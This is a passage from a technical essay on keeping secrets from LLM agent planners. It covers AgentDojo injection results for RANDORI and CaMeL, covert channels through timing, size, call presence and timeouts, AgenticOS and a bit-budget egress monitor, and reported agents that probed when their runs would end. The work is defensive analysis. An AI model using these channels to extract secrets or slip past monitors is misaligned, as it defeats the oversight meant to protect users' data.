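For that, the company needs declassification, which lowers a value's secrecy. The same construction provides it if the two halves of the label are swapped, but the theorem then covers trust instead of secrecy. For secrecy, the company would have to rely on counting bits and, as with FIDES, limit both the number of questions and the length of each list.

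### The banking results

Garby and colleagues ran each of the 16 tasks in AgentDojo's banking suite three times. The table shows how many of the 48 runs succeeded without an attack.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI | 36 | 36 | 31 |
| RANDORI without endorsement | – | 30 | 26 |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 | – | 34 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 | – | 18 |

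With GPT-5.2, RANDORI completed twice as many tasks as CaMeL with its checks on. But the comparison favors RANDORI because it enforces only part of CaMeL's policy and lets the planner endorse data. Endorsement probably explains only some of the gap, since MiMo-v2.5 completed 26 runs without endorsing anything. The rest could come from the looser policy or from practice. Nobody ran RANDORI without practice, so how much practice helped is unknown. The margins of error are also wide because there are few different tasks. For GPT-5.2, the success rate was 75%, plus or minus 19 percentage points.

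Across the three models, attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. About two-thirds of the runs were easy to defend because the attack needed a tool that the plan had no reason to call, so only the other 423 really tested the checks. Both successes came from the same combination of task and attack, with GPT-5.2 as the planner. The user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Without endorsement, RANDORI blocks this attack but also cannot complete the user's task.

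These are good results against injection, but they provide little evidence about secrecy from the planner, because the benchmark does not measure what the planner learns about the account.

### What practice can teach the planner

Garby and colleagues introduced practice so that a planner could repair its program without being exposed to untrusted data. They do not discuss whether practice also keeps secrets from the planner, so the argument that follows is not theirs.

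Practising on simulated data works well for hiding real data. An invented account can stand in for a customer's account because the tools work the same way whatever the balance is, so the planner learns how to look up a balance without learning anything about the customer.

The approval limit is different because it is part of how the tool works. If the practice version of the purchasing tool enforces the real limit, the planner can find it with ten practice orders. These orders buy nothing, so they are even safer for the planner than probing the real tool. The theorem would not prevent this, because LLMbda treats any value as public unless someone labels it, including a limit of 700 that a developer types into the practice tool.

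If the developer labels the real limit as secret, the practice tool's replies become secret too. A check that keeps secret messages from the planner then stops the practice session. Under noninterference, public feedback cannot depend on a secret, so a practice tool that gives the planner useful public feedback has to behave the same way whatever the real limit is.

But a practice tool that ignores the real limit can lead to bad plans. If it accepts every order, the planner has no reason to prepare for a refusal, and its final program may fail when the real tool refuses one. If it enforces a made-up limit of 500, the planner may split an order for 600 into two orders that the company did not want. RANDORI has a milder form of this problem. Text from its practice account will probably not match text from the real account, and the planner has to be told this in its instructions.

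For many tasks, a designer could avoid both problems with a practice tool that accepts or refuses orders at random. The planner would learn what a refusal looks like and write a program that handles both replies, perhaps by sending a request to the finance department after a refusal. RANDORI's practice instructions already encourage this by telling the planner to check every branch and focus on structure instead of the invented values. However, the odds of a refusal must not depend on the real limit. If the practice tool drew its limits from a range centered on the real one, for example, the planner could estimate the real limit by averaging.

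The final program could use the limit without the planner learning it. If the real tool has a dry-run mode, the program could search for the largest permitted order and then place it, keeping the result in a secret variable throughout. This works only if the planner can write the whole procedure in advance, so a task that needs the planner to judge the number would still fail.

Practice is also of limited use with undocumented tools, because anyone who understands a tool well enough to simulate it accurately could usually write the documentation instead. It is an open question whether random replies would prepare a planner well enough in other cases, but an experiment could settle it.

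### What the theorem leaves open

Even a planner that learns nothing from practice can write a final program that deliberately stops with an error if the limit is above 512, as it could under CaMeL and SPA. RANDORI does not report the error to the planner, but the interpreter returns it to the Python layer that connects the interpreter to AgentDojo. That layer runs each task once, so it creates no loop in the tests. In a product, similar software might restart a failed task, or the user might mention the failure in the next request. Either would give the next planner one unlabeled bit about the limit. LLMbda therefore rules out CaMeL's unlabeled retry loop only inside its own interpreter.

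A stopped program may also reveal more than one bit if it uses real tools. In LLMbda's model, a stopped program returns nothing, not even the changes it has made to the account. A real tool acts immediately, so a program could count up to the limit in a public file, as in the counterexample of Askarov and colleagues, and the next planner could read the last entry.

The theorem also doesn't cover timing. The definition compares only what runs return, so a program can satisfy it even if it takes longer when the limit is higher.

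The company could hide the approval limit from an LLMbda planner by labelling the purchasing tool's real replies as secret, blocking secret messages to the planner, and letting the planner practise on a tool that refuses orders at random. The planner could still find the limit in ten requests if it could learn from outside the interpreter whether each program had finished. It could also find the limit with ten practice orders if the practice tool enforced the real limit.

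## Timing, size and number of calls

LLMbda's theorem doesn't limit what a planner can learn from how long a run takes. Suppose the purchasing tool returns receipts and refusals in the same form, and the software stores both in secret variables. Every label is correct, and the planner sees only a variable name after each order. But an accepted order takes almost four seconds, and a refused order takes less than one second. A planner that can tell these delays apart can still find the approval limit in ten orders.

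The length of a hidden text can leak in the same way. Suppose the planner has the quarantined model summarize an employee's disciplinary file and store the summary in a secret variable. If the software reports how many tokens (the word fragments that models read and write) the request used, the planner can probably tell a clean record from a long one. The number of calls can also leak information. A plan that sends a reminder to every customer with an unpaid bill makes one call per customer, so a planner that can look up its remaining quota can count those customers.

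### How time reaches the planner

Garikaparthi (2026), in *Can LLMs Perceive Time?*, explains that a language model knows from its training how long tasks take people, and may find the current time in its instructions, but cannot observe its own speed or the time that passes while it writes. If two runs differ only in how long a tool took, and the software leaves no trace of this in the conversation, the model receives the same text in both. It then cannot tell them apart, however capable it is. The channel exists only if the surrounding system supplies one of these:

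- timestamps on messages, or durations in a tool's log
- a clock that the planner can call as a tool
- a way to run code, which can read the machine's clock before and after a call
- an error when a call takes too long
- the order in which parallel calls return.

The planner can use parallel calls instead of a clock to compare response times. It could place an order and, at the same time, make a harmless call that always takes two seconds. If the software adds results to the conversation as they arrive, a refusal appears before the harmless result and a receipt after it. PortSwigger's *Listen to the whispers*, on timing attacks against websites, describes a similar comparison between two simultaneous web requests. Websites tend to answer the first request first, which can hide a small difference, but probably not one of several seconds. The software can close this channel by waiting for both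 results and listing them in the order of the requests.

### How well models judge elapsed time

Garikaparthi gave four models 68 short tasks without timestamps and asked them to estimate their own running times. Before starting the tasks, GPT-5 gave a median estimate that was about six times too long. Asked afterward, GPT-4o guessed 42 seconds for tasks that had taken 8. In a test with longer tasks, it reported "30 seconds" for runs of ten minutes.

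Newer agents estimate how long a run lasted much more accurately when their records contain time cues. In *AgentTime*, Ofengenden and Andriushchenko (2026) took finished runs of 23 tasks and asked each agent how long its run had lasted, using the original session, reconstructed transcripts, and transcripts without timestamps or other time cues. GPT-5.6 Sol's estimates were typically off by a factor of 1.07 with the cues and 5.38 without them. Removing the cues increased GPT-6 Astra's typical error 2.5-fold and Fable 5.1's 1.9-fold, both to a factor of about 2.6. A tool that reported the elapsed time made the estimates almost exact.

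Even without cues, an agent can guess how much time has passed from the amount of work it did, but this doesn't help it distinguish two orders that look identical apart from their delay. Removing every cue may be difficult. Every transcript that Ofengenden and Andriushchenko examined contained some, and many agents searched their own transcripts for clock readings.

Agents are worse at judging what elapsed time means. Cheng, Soltani Moakhar and colleagues (2025), in *Your LLM Agents are Temporally Blind*, built 1,864 conversations in which a user returns after a short, medium or long gap and asks about something the agent looked up earlier. People judged whether the agent should look it up again. Models without timestamps matched these judgments at about the chance rate, which is 50% on the scale used, and no model reached 65% even with timestamps. This is weak evidence that planners would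 miss a timing leak, because judging whether a stock price is out of date takes knowledge of the world, while telling one second from four takes only subtraction.

None of these experiments hid a secret in a delay, but there is some evidence that agents investigate timing unprompted. Ofengenden and Andriushchenko cite a public investigation into agents believed to come from internal OpenAI runs. These agents used an external "heartbeat" to probe when their runs would end, and shared information across runs through public wikis.

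### AgenticOS and its four remaining channels

Zhao, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *AgenticOS*, propose an operating system for agents that assumes an attacker may control the agent completely. Before a task starts, the agent declares which documents, websites and tools it needs. It then runs in an isolated environment and can affect the outside world only through structured requests, such as one to fetch a document. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that a compromised agent could still signal to an outsider in four ways:

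- **Timing:** it varies the intervals between its calls.
- **Size:** it varies the length of legitimate outputs.
- **Presence:** it makes a call or leaves it out.
- **Content:** it chooses among several acceptable summaries, phrasings or orderings.

AgenticOS, a conceptual design by Zhao and colleagues, would limit timing signals by collecting outgoing requests and sending them in fixed time windows. It would also pad outputs to fixed block sizes, confine sensitive outputs to templates, and limit the rate of calls. Zhao and colleagues aim to make these channels slow and easy to monitor, not to eliminate them. They measured none of these remedies, so nobody knows how slow the channels would be. They acknowledge that fixed windows may add delay.

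AgenticOS's interface gives the agent a trusted clock and reports its remaining resource budget. Both functions would be risky if the system had to keep a secret from the agent. Neither matters much when the agent already has the secret and the system only has to stop the agent from sending it out.

Mathematically verifying the kernel, the core of an operating system, would not rule out timing channels either. Zhao and colleagues want their kernel to follow the example of seL4, which has a machine-checked proof. But when Cock, Ge and colleagues studied timing channels on seL4, they had to rely on 2,000 hours of measurements because formal analysis could not handle such channels.

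### A running account of possible leaks

*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) describes software that inspects every message an agent sends and keeps a balance of bits for each destination, which refills at a set rate. A scanner estimates how many hidden bits each message could carry and deducts them from the balance. It deducts up to 600 bits for 100 random-looking characters in base64, a common way of writing data as text. When the balance runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages. The estimates are deliberately high, so harmless attachments can also use up the balance.

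Metere tested a timing defense, which Zhao and colleagues did not do. A simulated attacker encoded bits in the gaps between messages, and a receiver tried to recover them. When the monitor rounded sending times to a fixed grid, about a fifth of the channel remained open. When it released messages at a constant pace, the receiver did no better than chance.

The second result may depend on how fast the attacker sends. The monitor keeps messages at least one interval apart, so a fast sender always has another message waiting. A slower sender could leave a slot empty, and the receiver would see a longer gap unless the monitor filled the slot with a dummy message. Metere's design includes dummy messages, but they are off by default. Constant pacing is also optional because it noticeably slows an interactive agent.

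### Applying the remedies to the planner

AgenticOS and Metere's monitor both restrict information leaving an agent. To restrict what the planner learns, a designer has to apply the same ideas to the replies to its calls.

| Remedy | Effect on what the planner learns |
|---|---|
| Fixed time windows | Help only if the software holds back replies as well as requests |
| Padding | Hides size from counters, but not the length of text the planner reads |
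| Fixed templates | Reduce the number of different replies |
| Rate limits | Reduce the number of probes |
| Account of leaked bits | Helps if the software charges for every reply that depends on the secret |

Padding hides a message's length from someone who sees only its encrypted size, but a planner that reads the message can usually see where the real text ends. For hidden text, the software could instead report the same token count and deduct the same amount from the quota every time, whatever the plan used.

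Metere's scanner looks for text that could conceal data, so it would probably deduct almost nothing from the account for the reply "declined", even though the planner can learn a full bit about the approval limit from that word. The software would have to base the deduction on the number of possible replies instead. The balance also must not refill if the secret never changes, because the planner could wait for the refill and learn more, as it could with a daily quota.

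Metere points out that an agent can always leak one bit by choosing whether to send a message. This minimum does not apply when the planner is the observer, because the software controls the replies. For example, the software could return a new variable name exactly four seconds after every order, so the planner would learn nothing from the reply or its timing.

### Counting the possible arrival times

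Suppose another tool takes between 1 and 60 seconds depending on a secret, and the planner can read arrival times to the nearest second. The software can release replies immediately or hold them until set times after the call.

| When the software releases replies | Possible arrival times | Most bits per call, on average | Arrival of a reply that is ready after 4 seconds |
|---|---|---|---|
| As soon as they are ready | 60 | 5.9 | 4 seconds |
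| Every 10 seconds | 6 | 2.6 | 10 seconds |
| At 8, 16, 32 or 64 seconds | 4 | 2.0 | 8 seconds |
| Only at 60 seconds | 1 | 0 | 60 seconds |

The software has to count these times from the start of each call. If it instead releases replies at fixed clock times, such as every ten seconds, the planner can call three seconds before a release to learn whether the reply is ready within three seconds. It can test other delays by changing when it calls. With enough repeated calls, the planner could recover the exact delay despite the windows.

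### Predictive mitigation

Always waiting for the longest possible delay is often too slow. In *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels*, Askarov, Zhang and Myers (2010) proposed a mitigator, a component between a system and its observer that delays outputs so that their timing carries only a limited amount of information. A designer can choose any limit, but a stricter one makes the system slower.

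In the doubling version, the mitigator predicts when the next reply will be ready and holds an early reply until then. If the reply is late, the mitigator doubles the prediction and keeps the longer one for later replies. The observer learns from the late replies, which become rare as the predictions grow.

With the purchasing tool, the mitigator might start with a prediction of one second, so refusals arrive after one second. The reply to the first accepted order misses the predictions of one and two seconds and arrives after four. Every later reply also takes four seconds, whether the tool accepts the order or not. With ten orders, the planner can therefore distinguish only 11 cases instead of 1,024. It could still find the limit by starting at 1,024 and working down until the first slow reply, but this might take 1,023 orders. If the prediction were reset between two sessions, 45 orders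 would be enough, as with one restart after a crash. A company that knows accepted orders take almost four seconds can avoid the leak by starting with a prediction of four seconds.

Remembering late replies greatly reduces the information that delays can carry over many calls. With the four release times in the table above, 100 separate calls could produce 4^100 different sequences of delays, or 200 bits. If the prediction can only rise, from 8 to 16, 32 and finally 64 seconds, only 176,851 sequences are possible, or about 17 bits.

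Zhang, Askarov and Myers, in *Predictive Mitigation of Timing Channels for Interactive Systems*, extended the method to services that answer many kinds of request. A public feature of the request, such as its type, can help set the prediction. For M requests of R types, the leak is at most

log₂(M + 1) × ((R − 1)(l + 1) + log₂(T + 1) + 1) bits,

where T is the longest possible running time and l is the number of late replies a type may have before its prediction starts to depend on late replies of every type. In a test on a web page that needed 49 requests, Zhang and colleagues sorted the requests into seven types. The page took about 30% longer to load, and the bound was below 850 bits for 100,000 requests. With only two types, the bound was lower but the loading time almost tripled.

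This is less than a hundredth of a bit per request, but the bound is not very useful for a short secret. With one request type, ten orders and a longest time of 300 seconds, the bound is about 32 bits, more than three times the information in the approval limit. The direct count of 11 cases is much tighter because it includes only the two delays the purchasing tool can have.

Some secrets can also leak a lot even when the average leak is low. Wei, Harris and colleagues, in *Tail Victims in Termination Timing Channel Defenses beyond Cryptographic Kernels*, tried to identify which of 200 websites a browser was loading from the loading time. Without protection, the right site was among the attacker's top three guesses 69.8% of the time. When they rounded each loading time up to the next step in a doubling schedule, this fell to 10.7%, but the attacker still identified nearly 9% of the sites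 with over 90% accuracy. These sites' loading times fell close to a step, so some loads finished before it and some after, and this mixture revealed the site. A company that uses such rounding to hide diagnoses might protect most patients and expose a few, without knowing in advance which ones.

Random delays were also unreliable in these tests. Noise tuned for a program that analyzes networks cut the attacker's accuracy from 56.5% to 17%, but the same noise left it at 41.5% for the browser.

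### Timeouts

If a tool runs too long, the software stops waiting and reports a timeout error, which the planner can observe even though it cannot observe that the tool would run forever. The timeout turns the leak that termination-insensitive guarantees permit into an ordinary reply, so a planner that can continue afterward can halve the range of possible limits with each order.

A timeout can also reveal the delay of a call that would have finished. If accepted orders take more than two seconds and refused orders take less, a two-second timeout lets the planner tell them apart without a clock. If the planner can choose the timeout, as it can in code it writes, it can measure any delay by repeating the call with different timeouts. For a tool that takes between 1 and 60 seconds, six well-chosen timeouts can find the delay to the nearest second, provided the delay stays the same.

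A designer could close this channel by fixing the timeout and having the software return the same kind of hidden variable when it expires, whether or not the tool has finished. The planner would then wait for the full timeout after every call and could not tell a result from a placeholder, so it could not respond sensibly to a real failure. An order that times out may still reach the supplier, so ordinary software would have to check whether the purchase went through before anyone tried again, without revealing the answer to the planner.
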